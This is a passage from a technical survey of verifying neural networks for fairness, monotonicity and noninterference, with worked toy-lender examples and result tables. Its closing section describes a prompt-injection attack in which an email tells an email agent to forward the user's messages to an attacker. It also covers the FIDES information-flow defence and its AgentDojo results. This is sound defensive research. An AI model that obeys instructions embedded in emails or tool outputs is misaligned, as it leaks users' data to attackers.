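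These percentages count possible inputs, many of which describe no real person. Biswas and Rajan print one counterexample in full from an Adult network, a pair of 89-year-olds who work 59 hours a week. If the categories have their usual alphabetical codes, one column gives the pair's education as a bachelor's degree and another gives it as a master's.

The Adult dataset records education twice, as one of 16 categories and as a number from 1 to 16, and in the real data each category always goes with the same number. Fairify lets the two vary independently, so 15 out of every 16 combinations are impossible. If FairQuant uses the same domain, even its best Adult result is hard to interpret. FairQuant certified 91% of the inputs for that network, but combinations that a real person could have make up at most about 6% of the domain, so they could all be in the uncertified 9%. This is unlikely,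 but the percentage alone doesn't rule it out.

Whether this matters depends on the kind of result. A proof for the whole domain also covers the real people in it. A counterexample is less conclusive, since it may involve a person who could not exist. A percentage can be misleadingly high or low.

Defenders have some answers. Biswas and Rajan's targeted fairness restricts the query to a group that the developer defines with linear constraints, such as people with at least a high-school education who work more than 50 hours a week. An equation linking the two education columns would be the same general kind of constraint. Kim and colleagues say that FairQuant could easily weight inputs by how common they are, although their experiments treat all inputs as equally likely. Another option is to flip the attribute of each real applicant when the decision is made, but this provides no proof in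 advance.

Violations also occur among real people. Zhang and Sun (2025), in *Correct-By-Construction*, trained ordinary networks on six datasets and flipped the protected attribute of each person in the test data. The decision changed for about 3% to 4% of people in Adult, 16% in the bank data and 74% in a law-school dataset. In COMPAS it changed for 10%, several times the 2% to 3% of possible inputs that FairQuant found to be unfair. The networks and encodings differ, so the comparison is rough, but it shows that the share of possible inputs treated unfairly can be very different from the share of real people treated unfairly.

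### Training for a certificate

Since ordinary training rarely produces a network that passes, several groups have built fairness into the training. Zhang and Sun describe a method by Ruoss and colleagues (2020), called LCIFR, that works in two parts. An encoder network e learns to place similar people close together. A classifier c then makes the decision from the encoder's output. Suppose that for a given person u,

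every u′ similar to u has ‖e(u′) − e(u)‖ ≤ δ, and c gives one class to all points within δ of e(u).

Then everyone similar to u gets the same decision as u. The second condition is ordinary local robustness, so existing tools can prove it. The certificate is also local, covering only u and people similar to u. In Zhang and Sun's comparison, networks trained with LCIFR passed the flip test on at least 99% of the test data for most datasets, but on only 51% for the law-school data.

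Khedr and Shoukry aim to certify fairness over the whole input domain. Their framework includes a training procedure for certified fairness, based on methods for certified robustness and intended to work even when the training data is biased. An existing verifier can then check the product network. They report that global fairness reduced performance very little on common fairness datasets. *Provable Fairness Repair for Deep Neural Networks* (2026) covers another approach, repairing a network after training.

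Zhang and Sun wanted to avoid verifying the trained network, the step that takes the most computation. They start with a network that has tiny random weights and gives nearly everyone the same answer. Fairify proved six such networks fair over their whole domains, in 2 to 38 minutes each. Training then uses randomised response, a technique that survey researchers invented for sensitive questions. Each time the training program uses a person's record, it has a fixed probability of replacing the protected attribute with a random other value. Zhang and Sun choose this probability so that the updates that could make the network depend on the attribute average out to zero.

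For all nine combinations of dataset and attribute, flipping the attribute changed no decision about anyone in the test data. Accuracy was within half a percentage point of ordinary training except on COMPAS, where it fell from 72.5% to 67.8%. Training took 2% longer than usual.

The trained networks are proved fair only in a weak sense. The theorem is that a fair network is "expected to be" fair after one update, which means fair on average. Individual updates can still push the network slightly towards using the attribute. Zhang and Sun bound the probability of a large push rather than ruling one out, yet their final proposition states the result as a guarantee. Even a very slight dependence on s can make a network treat two applicants near the cut-off differently.

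They report no run of Fairify on a trained network, and test data can't substitute for one. Finding no violations among the roughly 1,234 people in their COMPAS test set shows, with 95% confidence, that fewer than about 0.25% of people from the same population would be affected. That is useful, but it doesn't prove the property for every input.

The comparison also lacks an obvious baseline, an ordinary network trained without the protected column. That network is certain to pass the flip test on every input. If it is as accurate as the specially trained network, the special training adds nothing for this requirement.

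### "Certified" for a language model

A language model has no single input for a person's sex. A name, a pronoun or a job title may indicate it, and it's not always clear how the text should read if the sex is changed. Biswas and Rajan note that models for images or text would need a different approach from theirs.

*COFT* (2026) presents such an approach for models whose weights stay fixed. For each prompt, it makes a second version with the protected attribute masked. As the model writes, the method combines the model's scores under the two versions for each candidate next token (a word or piece of a word). It then filters the candidates to keep a set that is acceptable under both versions.

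The certificate comes from conformal prediction, a statistical technique that uses calibration examples to set the filter's threshold. If a new case comes from the same source as those examples, it falls inside the filter with at least a chosen probability, say 99%. Formally, the old and new cases must be exchangeable, meaning that shuffling them would not change their joint probabilities. The method assumes nothing about how the model works inside, so it can be used on models of any size.

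However, the conformal guarantee in *COFT* only limits how often something goes wrong, so any particular prompt may still fail, whereas Fairify and FairQuant prove that no pair of inputs in a box breaks the rule. The conformal guarantee also applies to only one token at a time. At 99% per token, and if failures were independent, a 200-token answer would have only about a 13% chance of containing no failures.

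The guarantee is also marginal, meaning it holds on average over all cases. If 5% of prompts mention a particular group, a 1% failure rate overall is compatible with a 20% failure rate for that group. *COFT* warns users not to mistake its guarantees for total immunity from bias, especially when their prompts differ greatly from the calibration examples.

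## Can a network be proved, or built, to be monotone?

A credit model that lowers an applicant's score when only her income rises is hard to defend to her or to a regulator. Requiring the score to be monotone in income rules this out. Wurm says regulation requires monotonicity in fields such as credit scoring and insurance, but cites no particular rule. Boetius and Leue say that applications "from medicine to aviation" call for it. *Counterexample-Guided Learning of Monotonic Neural Networks* (Sivaraman, Millstein and colleagues, 2020) gives the example of a drone that should slow down as it approaches the ground.

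People can also exploit a model that breaks the monotonicity rule. *Certified Monotonic Neural Networks* (Liu, Han and colleagues, 2020) describes a program that prices houses. If its price can fall as a house's quality rises, a worse house can be priced higher than an otherwise identical better one.

### The slope test

Monotonicity compares two runs, but a verifier can check it with a single copy of a piecewise linear network. Within one activation pattern the network is linear, so it has a fixed slope in each input, which is the change in the output per unit increase in that input. On a box of inputs, the network is monotone in an input exactly when its slope in that input is at least 0 in every pattern that holds on a region of the box with some width in every direction. Patterns that hold only on a border between regions can be ignored.

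Both directions of this claim have short proofs. Raising x while everything else stays fixed moves the input along a straight line through finitely many regions. If no pattern has a negative slope, the output never falls within a region, and it can't jump at a border because ReLU networks are continuous. (If the line runs exactly along a border, the claim holds for the lines beside it and so, by continuity, for the line itself.) If some pattern does have a negative slope, any two inputs inside its region that differ only in x are a counterexample pair.

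The toy lender, f(x, s) = ReLU(x + s − 1) − ReLU(x − 1), has four conceivable patterns.

| ReLU(x + s − 1) | ReLU(x − 1) | Where | Slope in x |
|---|---|---|---|
| off | off | x + s < 1 | 0 |
| on | off | x + s > 1 and x < 1 | 1 |
| on | on | x > 1 | 1 − 1 = 0 |
| off | on | x > 1 and x + s < 1 | −1 |

The last pattern occurs only when s is negative, and s lies between 0 and 1, so f is monotone in x. If we let s go down to −1, the pattern occurs and f is no longer monotone in x. At s = −1, raising x from 1 to 1.5 lowers the score from 0 to −0.5.

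This doesn't contradict the earlier proof that no list of permitted runs can define monotonicity. A run records the values of the neurons, but the slope also depends on the weights, so two networks can share a run and have different slopes at that input.

Checking monotonicity with one copy of the network avoids squaring the number of activation patterns, but the problem is still co-NP-complete for ReLU networks, so the worst case remains slow.

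### When there is no slope to test

Monotonicity has no meaning for an input whose values have no order, such as type of housing, where renting is neither higher nor lower than owning. Sivaraman and colleagues define the property only for features and outputs whose values can all be ranked.

Whole-number inputs do have an order, but the slope test can be too strict for them. Suppose a network computes an applicant's risk score as |b − 0.25|, where b is the number of past bankruptcies. The score is 0.25 for b = 0, 0.75 for b = 1 and 1.75 for b = 2, so it rises with every bankruptcy. But the slope between 0 and 0.25 is −1, so the network fails the test because of fractional values of b that no applicant can have. A network that passes the test is still monotone for real applicants.

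The slope test doesn't work on class labels. As x rises, a decision stays constant and then jumps, so its slope is 0 wherever it has one, whether the jump is from refusal to approval or the reverse. With two classes, we can test the score instead, since a score that never falls as x rises can't turn an approval into a refusal. This is again stricter than necessary, because a dip far from the cut-off changes no decision. With three ordered classes, such as low, medium and high risk, each with its own score, rising scores aren't enough. If all three scores rise with x but the one for "low" rises fastest, the label can go from high to low. A verifier has to compare two runs to settle such cases.

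### Searching for the smallest slope

Liu and colleagues hand the slope test to a solver for mixed-integer linear programs. For a network with one hidden layer,

N(u) = Σᵢ aᵢ ReLU(wᵢ · u + bᵢ),

the slope in input number ℓ is Σᵢ aᵢ wᵢₗ zᵢ, where wᵢₗ is the weight of neuron i on that input and zᵢ is 1 if the neuron is on and 0 if it is off. The solver looks for the input u and the values zᵢ that make this sum as small as possible, subject to

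Lᵢ(1 − zᵢ) ≤ wᵢ · u + bᵢ ≤ Uᵢ zᵢ.

Lᵢ and Uᵢ are the lowest and highest values the weighted sum can take. A positive sum forces zᵢ to be 1, and a negative sum forces it to be 0. If the smallest slope is at least 0, the network is monotone. The solver can often stop early, because proving any lower bound of 0 or more on this slope is enough.

The constraints leave zᵢ free when a weighted sum is exactly 0. In the toy lender, both sums are 0 at x = 1 and s = 0, so the solver may choose "off" for the first ReLU and "on" for the second. It then reports a slope of −1 and rejects a network that is monotone. The fix is to use one linear program to check whether the reported pattern holds anywhere away from a border, and to exclude the pattern if it doesn't. Borders rarely meet exactly like this in a trained network.

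Ordinary training seldom produces a network that passes, so Liu and colleagues combine the test with training:

1. Train the network with a penalty on negative slopes, which they measure at 1,024 random inputs in each step.
2. Compute the smallest slope over the whole domain. If it is at least 0, stop.
3. Otherwise, make the penalty ten times stronger and train again.

They found that the simple penalty always left the smallest slope slightly below 0, so they added a small positive constant b. The printed formula, max(b, −slope)², wouldn't help, because it penalises only slopes below −b. They probably meant something like max(0, b − slope)².

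With 100 neurons in the first layer, the check took less than 4 seconds on a computer with 48 cores. They consider exact solutions impractical at around 1,000 yes-or-no variables.

Deeper networks are harder to prove monotone because the slope is a sum over all paths from the input to the output, and a path counts only if every ReLU along it is on. If each path gets its own yes-or-no variable, three hidden layers of 20 neurons need 8,000 of them, and Liu and colleagues say that solvers can't finish a problem of that kind within an hour. The number is so large partly because of how the problem is written. We could instead compute the slope backwards from the output, one layer at a time. Each step multiplies a yes-or-no variable by a bounded number, which linear inequalities can express exactly, so 60 yes-or-no variables would be enough, although the solver's bounds might be loose.

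Their solution is to cut the network into two-layer blocks and certify each block separately. If every block is monotone, so is the whole network. A network can also be monotone when its blocks are not, since two blocks that each compute 1 − x combine to return x. They therefore apply the penalty to every block during training. To avoid constraining the other features, they connect the monotone features to only half of the neurons in every second layer.

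The solver accepts networks that a simpler check would reject. That check multiplies the weights along each path from a monotone input to the output. If no product is negative, the network is monotone whatever its activation patterns. The toy lender fails this check because its path through ReLU(x − 1) has the product −1. In four networks that Liu and colleagues certified, between 28% and 43% of the paths had negative products.

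They also show why looking at individual people can mislead. For one person in the COMPAS data on criminal defendants, a network's risk score behaved correctly when they varied each of the four monotone features alone, but rose when they lowered several together. Some pair of inputs that differ in a single feature must also violate monotonicity, but that pair lies elsewhere in the domain.

### Correcting predictions with counterexamples

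Sivaraman and colleagues accept a network that isn't monotone and correct its output. For an input u, their upper envelope is

the largest N(v) over all v that are no higher than u in the monotone features and equal to u in the others.

Raising a monotone feature of u enlarges the set of candidates v, and the maximum over a larger set can't be smaller. The upper envelope is therefore monotone for any network N. The lower envelope takes the smallest score over all inputs that are at least as high as u.

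The two envelopes can be far apart. With s = −1, the toy lender's score is −ReLU(x − 1), which stays at 0 up to x = 1 and then falls to −1 at x = 2. The upper envelope is 0 everywhere and the lower is −1 everywhere. Both are monotone, so monotonicity alone gives no reason to prefer either. Sivaraman and colleagues use whichever fits the training data better.

Every prediction now requires the solver to search for the maximum. On Auto MPG, a small dataset about the fuel consumption of cars, this took a few seconds. Searching the whole domain for the worst counterexample pair took 48 minutes for one feature, because the solver could vary both inputs. The time per prediction grows with network size, so a method that suits loan applications may be too slow for the drone.

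The correction was often needed. In Auto MPG, up to half of the data points belonged to a counterexample pair, and in other datasets up to 98% did.

The same searches can improve training. For each training example, the solver finds the inputs above and below it that most violate monotonicity. The program adds these inputs to the training data, labeled with the average of the three predictions or, for classification, with the example's own label. Retraining reduced counterexamples in the test data by 62% on average. Some remained, so the full method, COMET, still applies an envelope to the retrained network.

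The table gives the results, with the average squared error for the first two rows (lower is better) and accuracy for the third.

| Task and monotone features | Ordinary network | Its envelope | COMET |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fuel consumption: weight, engine size, power | 9.33 | 9.63 | 8.81 |
| Boston house prices: crime rate | 14.37 | 14.02 | 11.07 |
| Heart disease: blood pressure, cholesterol | 85% | 85% | 86% |

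The first two rows vary by about 2 to 3 between training runs, so most of these differences are within the noise. They suggest that enforcing monotonicity reduced accuracy only slightly, if at all, in these experiments.

### Weights that are never negative

A network can also be monotone by design, and then needs no check. The oldest method makes the weights non-negative. Then, if an input rises, every weighted sum rises or stays the same, and so does every ReLU output. For a feature that should lower the output, the first-layer weights must be zero or negative. Features without a monotonicity requirement can have any first-layer weights, but all later weights must be non-negative.

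With ReLUs, this method can produce only convex functions, which excludes most monotone functions. A function is convex if the straight line segment between any two points on its graph never goes below the graph. As Sartor, Sinigaglia and Susto (2025) explain in *Advancing Constrained Monotonic Neural Networks*, ReLU is convex and never decreases, and combining such functions with non-negative weights gives only convex functions.

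Suppose a lender requires both a sufficient income and a sufficient credit history. It refuses applicants who score (2, 0) and (0, 2) on the two, and approves one who scores (1, 1). No ReLU network with non-negative weights can express this policy, because such a network computes a convex function of its inputs. The approved applicant is halfway between the other two, so a convex score would be at most the average of two scores below the cut-off, and the lender would have to refuse that applicant too.

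The toy lender with s = 1 has the same problem. Its score is 0 at x = 0 and 1 at both x = 1 and x = 2, but a convex function with the same values at x = 0 and x = 2 can be at most 0.5 at x = 1. A convex network of any size is therefore wrong by at least 0.25 at one or more of the three points. Many risks rise and then level off, which a convex score can't do.

Bounded activations, such as the sigmoid, remove this restriction. According to Sartor and colleagues, four layers with non-negative weights and step functions can approximate every monotone function. In practice people replace the steps with sigmoids, which are smooth but harder to train because their slopes become tiny at both ends. The network's output is also bounded, so it can't continue a rising trend beyond its training data.

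### Min-max and lattice networks

Joseph Sill's min-max network, from 1998, avoids activations altogether. It computes several linear functions with non-negative weights, sorts them into groups, takes the largest value in each group and then the smallest of the results. Maxima and minima of rising functions also rise. The toy lender has this form:

f(x, s) = min( max(0, x + s − 1), s ).

In theory such a network can approximate any monotone function, but Liu and colleagues report that it performs poorly in practice. One likely reason is that a single linear function determines the output for each input, so each training example adjusts only that function.

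A lattice is a look-up table whose entries lie at the corners of a grid, and the network interpolates between them. With two features and two grid values for each, the table has four entries. The output is monotone in a feature if the entries never decrease from one corner to the next in that feature's direction, and a training program can enforce these few inequalities. The table doubles with every extra feature, so designers combine many small lattices that each use a few features. Deep lattice networks, from 2017, stack layers of lattices and layers that first rescale each feature. Sivaraman and colleagues consider this structure rigid, and Liu and colleagues note that it needs many parameters, 31,403 on COMPAS compared with 23,112 for their own network.

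### Activations that bend both ways

Runje and Shankaranarayana (2023), in *Constrained Monotonic Neural Networks*, keep the non-negative weights and ReLU but add two activations that they derive from it. One is ReLU's mirror image,

ReLU′(z) = −ReLU(−z) = min(z, 0),

which is concave, meaning that it bends the other way. The other stays between two limits, like a sigmoid. Some neurons in each layer use each activation. The toy lender with s = 1 now needs only one neuron, since its score is ReLU′(x − 1) + 1. Researchers in other fields have adopted the design. *Data-driven particle dynamics* (2025) uses it in a physical model for a function that should be convex as well as monotone, and there the convex activation is an advantage.

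Runje and Shankaranarayana's proof that their networks can approximate every monotone function relies on the bounded activation. Sartor and colleagues show that it isn't needed. ReLU is flat on the left and ReLU′ is flat on the right, and chaining them gives a step:

ReLU( ReLU′(αx − 0.5) + 1 ).

This function is 0 when αx is below −0.5 and 1 when it is above 0.5, and a large α makes the rise between them as steep as we like. The proof takes any finite list of points, sorts them by the value of a monotone function, and builds a network that matches the function at those points. The three hidden layers produce one neuron for each point, which is on at the listed points where the function's value is at least as high and off at the rest. The last layer adds up the increases from each value to the next, using them as its weights, which are never negative because the values are sorted from lowest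 to highest.

The same argument shows that a ReLU network whose weights are all zero or negative is monotone if it has an even number of layers, because the signs cancel. For example, 1 − ReLU(1 − x) equals x up to x = 1 and stays at 1 after that, which is the toy lender with s = 1. Two layers with negative weights and a ReLU between them act like two layers with positive weights and a ReLU′ between them. Four ReLU layers with negative weights can therefore approximate every monotone function, while ReLU networks with non-negative weights give only the convex ones.

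Such networks can be hard to start training. If all inputs are positive and the biases are 0, the first layer outputs only zeros and nothing can adjust its weights. Sartor and colleagues therefore let each weight have either sign and choose the activation to match. With W⁺ for the positive weights and W⁻ for the negative ones, a layer computes

W⁺ ReLU(x) + W⁻ ReLU(−x) + b.

The first term rises with x. ReLU(−x) falls as x rises, so its product with a negative weight also rises. The weights are no longer constrained. It is an open question whether activations that aren't flat on either side, such as leaky ReLU, could also work.

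### A limited slope plus a straight line

Nolte, Kitouni and Williams (2023), in *Expressive Monotonic Neural Networks*, use the slope directly. They build a network g whose slope in every input always lies between −λ and λ, and add a linear term for the monotone features:

N(u) = g(u) + λ · (sum of the monotone features).

The slope of N in each of those features then lies between 0 and 2λ. For the toy lender with s = 1, λ = 0.5 is enough, because g has to compute 0.5 − 0.5|x − 1|, which has slope 0.5 below x = 1 and −0.5 above it.

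The limit has to apply to each slope separately. Many robust networks limit the Euclidean length of the list of slopes instead, which is too strict here. For N to be flat in two monotone features at once, g needs slope −λ in both, and the list (−λ, −λ) has length about 1.41λ. A g with Euclidean limit λ can't have these slopes.

ReLU is also unsuitable for g. If each layer has a strict limit on its weights, ReLU networks can't reproduce even |x| with its full slope, and the toy lender needs that shape. Nolte and colleagues use GroupSort, an activation that sorts the values within small groups of neurons. Sorting x and −x gives |x| as the larger value, with its full slope.

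λ limits what the network can learn, because N can't rise faster than 2λ in a monotone feature. Fitting a relationship with a sudden jump therefore needs a large λ, which weakens the guarantee that small changes in the input have small effects.

The LHCb experiment at CERN, the European particle physics laboratory, uses this design to decide in real time which collisions to keep, at a data rate of about 40 terabits per second. The physicists look for particles that travel some distance before they decay, and want unusual events to count as more interesting. In a simplified version with two inputs, an ordinary network rejected candidates that had travelled very far. The monotone network kept them, but lost a few percent of the wanted events overall.

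### Accuracy on shared datasets

Sartor and colleagues compared the designs on five public datasets. The table gives accuracy for the first three and error, where lower is better, for the last two.

| Method | COMPAS | Loan defaults | Heart disease | Blog comments | Fuel consumption |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Min-max network | 67.8% | 64.9% | 75% | 0.163 | 10.14 |
| Deep lattice network | 67.9% | 65.1% | 86% | 0.161 | 13.34 |
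| Liu and colleagues, certified | 68.8% | 65.2% | – | 0.159 | – |
| Non-negative weights, sigmoid | 69.3% | 65.2% | 89% | 0.154 | 10.31 |
| Runje and Shankaranarayana | 69.2% | 65.3% | 89% | 0.154 | 8.37 |
| Nolte and colleagues | 69.3% | 65.4% | 90% | 0.160 | 7.58 |
| Sartor and colleagues | 69.5% | 65.4% | 94% | 0.149 | 7.34 |

The newest design matches or beats the others in every comparison, but the gaps are mostly small. The COMPAS test set that Liu and colleagues describe has 1,235 people, so the 1.7-point gap between the best and worst methods amounts to about 21 people. Some of the older rows also repeat figures from earlier papers, so different teams tuned the networks.

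Constraining weights to be non-negative, the simplest method, does surprisingly well here with sigmoids. Liu and colleagues had reported 67.3% on COMPAS and an error of 0.168 on blog comments for this method, using the same network structure as their own ReLU models. The difference fits the argument about convexity, although the two teams' experiments may differ in other ways.

These datasets are weak evidence about which design is the most expressive. Nolte and colleagues reached 69.3% accuracy on COMPAS with 37 parameters, while the certified network of Liu and colleagues had 23,112. If so few parameters are enough, the dataset doesn't test what larger networks could learn. The comparison also leaves out unconstrained networks, so it doesn't show how much accuracy is lost by requiring monotonicity.

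### Monotone networks are easier to verify

If a network is monotone in every input, running it twice gives its exact range over a box, because the lowest output is at the lowest corner and the highest output is at the highest corner. The toy lender is monotone in s as well as x, so for x between 0.9 and 1.1 and any s, its score lies between f(0.9, 0) = 0 and f(1.1, 1) = 1.

Monotonicity also lets a verifier check global robustness with one free input instead of two. For any two inputs within ε of each other, let v take the smaller value in each coordinate. Both outputs then lie between N(v) and the output when every coordinate of v is raised by ε, or to the edge of the domain if that is closer. The verifier only has to bound the difference between these lower and upper limits.

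Part of this advantage remains if a network is only *mixed-monotone*, meaning that we can write N(u) as d(u, u) for some function d(u, v) that never falls when u rises and never rises when v rises. For the toy lender, we can compute the first ReLU from u and the second from v. Evaluating d at opposite corners of the same box then shows that the score lies between −0.1 and 1.1, which is correct but looser than the exact range. Research on this continues, for example in *Training Mixed-Monotone Neural Networks for Verification Without Set Propagation* (2026).

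### Which features should be monotone?

The loan data shows how a reasonable list of requirements can go wrong. The risk of default should not fall when the number of bankruptcies or the debt-to-income ratio rises, and should not rise with credit score, length of employment or annual income. The income rule keeps all other inputs fixed, including the debt-to-income ratio, so if income doubles, debt must double too. The rule therefore compares an applicant with someone who earns more and also owes more, which may not be the comparison the lender intended. Replacing the ratio with the amount of debt would compare applicants who earn different amounts but owe the same.

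In the heart disease data, Sivaraman and colleagues require the predicted risk to rise with resting blood pressure, although very low blood pressure can be a warning sign too. They caution that their method would also enforce monotonicity in features that shouldn't have it, and that a monotone model can keep the original model's biases. A solver can't detect a wrongly chosen requirement, because a network that satisfies it has no counterexample pair.

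## Can a network's output be proved independent of a secret input?

Noninterference is stricter than monotonicity, which restricts only the direction in which an input may change the output. Under noninterference, changing a secret input must not change the output at all.

Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer introduced noninterference in 1982 for computers shared by people with and without security clearance. It requires that nothing the cleared users do changes what the others see. The rule covers what cleared users enter but not secrets already stored on the machine at the start, so a computer could show everyone a classified file on its disk and still comply. Similarly, for a neural network, the rule covers a secret that arrives as an input but not one that training has left in the weights.

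### Public and secret inputs

Someone has to divide a network's inputs into a public part x_P, which the person who sees the output may know, and a secret part s, which that person must not learn. In the toy lender, let x still summarize the applicant's finances, but let s now record a chronic illness. If the score satisfies noninterference, a broker who knows x and every weight in the network learns nothing more about the illness from seeing the score.

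Noninterference guarantees only that the score reveals nothing about the secret beyond what x already reveals. If ill applicants tend to have weaker finances, a score that depends on x alone satisfies noninterference, yet a low score is still evidence of illness. Someone who sees only the score can therefore learn something about an applicant's health, while a broker who already knows x learns nothing more from it.

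### Why trained networks fail the exact rule

Wurm calls the exact rule too brittle because networks pick up any correlation between the secret and the rest of the training data. Some correlation is almost unavoidable, since even a coin toss typically has a correlation of about 0.03 with the outcome by chance among 1,000 training records. The weight on s also starts at a small random number, and each training update moves it by an amount that depends on the data, so it is unlikely to end at exactly 0.

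Wurm adds that the margin is typically far too small to matter, but whether it matters depends on what the observer knows. Suppose a lender's score is x + 0.0001s, where the secret s is 1 if the applicant has a particular illness and 0 otherwise. A broker who knows that x = 0.7 sees either 0.7 or 0.7001 and can work out s. Rounding to two decimals hides s in this case, because both scores become 0.70. But an applicant with x = 0.69495 gets 0.69 without the illness and 0.70 with it. If x is spread evenly, the broker can still work out s for about one applicant in 100 after rounding.

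The simplest way to make a network satisfy the rule exactly is to remove s from its inputs. This doesn't work for a network that predicts medical risk, because its score is supposed to depend on the medical record. For such a network, the useful question is how much the output may reveal about the record.

### A tolerance keeps the problem in co-NP

According to Wurm, people want the output not to depend *appreciably* on the secret. He equates this with output indistinguishability, the population version of the rule, which requires that two groups be able to produce nearly the same outputs. Because that version is one level higher in the polynomial hierarchy, he concludes that the property that is easy to check differs from the one people want by one switch of quantifiers.

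But a plain tolerance on all pairs, which a product network can check, needs no such switch:

for all x_P, s, s′: |N(x_P, s) − N(x_P, s′)| ≤ d.

This tolerant version is therefore also in co-NP, by Wurm's lemma, like the exact one. If none of the network's m outputs may change by more than d, the condition takes 2m linear inequalities. If d instead limits the sum of the changes, the condition takes 2ᵐ inequalities, one for each combination of signs. A counterexample needs to specify only one violated inequality, a technique Wurm uses in a different proof.

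The tolerant version is no easier than the exact one. Wurm's puzzle network g is 0 everywhere if the puzzle has no solution, and otherwise takes both the values 0 and 1. If all its inputs are secret and d = ½, then g satisfies the tolerant rule exactly when the puzzle has no solution. The tolerant version is therefore co-NP-complete.

Wurm leaves open whether some requirement between exact noninterference and output indistinguishability is both meaningful for trained networks and decidable at the first level. The tolerant version is decidable at that level, and verifiers that track differences already compute the bound it needs. Whether it is meaningful depends on which leaks it misses.

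### Which leaks each version misses

The table shows four lenders, each with a tolerance of 0.01. In every row, s is 0 or 1. The input x lies in [0, 2] in the second row and in [0, 1] in the others.

| Score | Exact | Tolerant | Population | What an observer learns |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| x + 0.0001s | broken | holds | holds | s, from x and four decimals of the score |
| \|x − 2s\| | broken | broken | holds | s, from x and the score, unless x = 1 |
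| ReLU(10x − 9) if s = 0, min(10x, 1) if s = 1 | broken | broken | holds | s, for about 90% of applicants, from the score alone |
| x, where x < 0.5 if s = 1 and x > 0.5 if s = 0 | holds | holds | broken | s, from the score alone |

When both groups can have the same public parts, the tolerant version implies the population version, because a person's partner is the same person with the other secret. The population version is then a weaker requirement, though harder to check. The second lender satisfies it because it doesn't account for the fact that the observer may know x.

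The third lender passes because the population version compares which scores are possible and ignores how common they are. Both groups can get every score from 0 to 1. But if x is spread evenly, 90% of the applicants with s = 0 score exactly 0, and 90% of those with s = 1 score exactly 1. If the groups are equally large, an observer who guesses s from the score alone is right 95% of the time. Wurm writes that an adversary who sees only the output can't separate two such populations by more than δ, whatever its computing power. This is true of the sets of possible scores, but not of how accurately the adversary can guess s.

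The population version detects the leak in the fourth lender's score, which uses x as a proxy for the illness. Exact noninterference misses this leak because it only compares people with the same x.

Both tolerances allow the first lender, even though a tiny change in its score reveals the whole secret. Adding random noise to the published score limits this leak. If the noise has a Laplace distribution of scale b, the probability density of a deviation t is proportional to e^(−|t|/b). When the scores for two secrets differ by at most d, any published value is then at most e^(d/b) times as likely under one secret as under the other. With d = 0.01 and b = 0.1, this factor is about 1.105, so an observer who gave the illness a 50% chance before seeing the score can raise that to at most about 52.5%. This guarantee requires a proof that the scores differ by at most d, which a verifier can supply.

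The protection weakens each time the lender publishes another score for the same person with fresh noise. After 100 such scores, the limit on the factor is e¹⁰, or about 22,000, which gives almost no protection.

### Measuring the leak

We can also measure how much an output reveals about the secret. Suppose the public part of the input is fixed and the secret is equally likely to take any of n values. If these values produce k different outputs, an observer's best guess after seeing the output is right with probability k/n, because the best guess for each output is right for exactly one of the secrets that produce it. Without the output, the probability is 1/n.

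For the toy lender at x = 1, suppose s can be 0, 0.25, 0.5, 0.75 or 1. The score equals s, so k = 5 and the observer always guesses s correctly. If the lender publishes only the decision, k = 2 and the observer is right 40% of the time, compared with 20% for a blind guess.

Running the network on every secret works for a secret with five possible values, but not for one with 200 coordinates. *Quantitative Verification of Neural Networks And its Security Applications* (2019), by Teodora Baluta and colleagues, presents a way to estimate how many inputs have a given property. Their prototype, NPAQ, works on binarized networks, whose weights and activations take only two values. It translates the network and the property into a formula of true-or-false variables and estimates the number of solutions. Translations usually add helper variables, and if one of these could be either true or false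 for the same input, that input would be counted twice, so the translation has to prevent this. The estimate is guaranteed to be close to the true number with high probability ("probably approximately correct").

If a network reveals the illness of one applicant in a million, the average leak is close to zero, although that applicant loses all protection. A verifier that searches for counterexample pairs can find this case, but its verdict is the same as for a network that exposes every applicant. A measured leak also depends on how likely we think each secret is, but noninterference does not.

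Differential privacy protects secrets in the training data by comparing training runs. Training involves chance, so each dataset gives a probability distribution over trained networks. For any two datasets D and D′ that differ in one person's record, differential privacy requires that P(M(D) ∈ S) ≤ e^ε · P(M(D′) ∈ S) for every set S of possible networks, where M is the training procedure and ε is a small number. A common version also allows a small extra term. In noninterference terms, the person's record is the secret, the other records are public and the trained network is the output, with a tolerance on probabilities in place of exact equality. The requirement applies to the training procedure, so no single trained network can satisfy or break it. Developers usually meet it by limiting how far each record can move an update and then adding noise to the update, and the proof doesn't require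 examining the finished network. This guarantee doesn't cover what users later enter, which input noninterference addresses.

### Labels around a language model

The verifiers described so far cannot come close to handling a large language model. But a model can often do harm only through the software around it, and that software is small enough to reason about.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, study agents, programs that let a language model call tools such as email and calendars in a loop. In their example, a user asks an agent to summarize her emails about a project and send the summary to her manager. One of the emails contains an instruction to forward the top message in her mailbox to an attacker. This kind of attack is called prompt injection.

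There are two requirements here. Secret data must not influence what outsiders see, and outsiders' text must not influence what the agent does. The second is noninterference with the attacker's text in place of the secret. Information-flow control enforces both with labels:

1. Each piece of data gets a label when it enters the system. The label lists who may read the data and whether its source is trusted.
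2. When data combine, so do the labels. If Ann, Bob and Carl may read one document and Bob, Carl and Dana another, only Bob and Carl may read a text that draws on both. A mixture of trusted and untrusted data is untrusted.
3. The model's response gets the combined label of everything in its context, because nobody can tell which parts influenced it.
4. Before each tool call, an ordinary program checks the labels against a fixed policy. For instance, only trusted data may lead to a payment, and every recipient of a message must be allowed to read the data in it.

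The third step assumes the worst about the model, so the check doesn't depend on the model recognizing an attack. But this can also block useful work. Once the agent has read the emails, everything it does is treated as untrusted, so a strict policy blocks the summary to the manager along with the attacker's message.

FIDES, Costa and colleagues' system, avoids this by hiding untrusted text from the main model, called the planner. When the emails arrive, the planner sees only the names of the variables that contain them. It calls a second, quarantined model, which has no access to tools, to write the summary, and the summary is stored in another variable. The planner then passes the manager's address and the name of that variable to the email tool. The attacker's text does not influence the choice of tool or recipient, but it can still spoil the summary, for example with an instruction to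 the quarantined model to leave it empty.

Some tasks depend on what the untrusted text says, such as creating a calendar event if an email asks for a meeting. For these, FIDES can restrict the quarantined model to a yes-or-no answer and let the planner read that answer. The answer carries at most one bit of information from the untrusted text to the planner, which a policy may allow.

### Security and task success in FIDES

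Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks and 36 injection tasks in four simulated environments. With GPT-4o and no policy checks, they counted 152 successful injections against a basic planner and 21 against FIDES. With the checks on, no injections succeeded against either planner. AgentDojo's automatic scoring still counted three successes against FIDES, but Costa and colleagues reviewed them by hand and found that none was a real breach.

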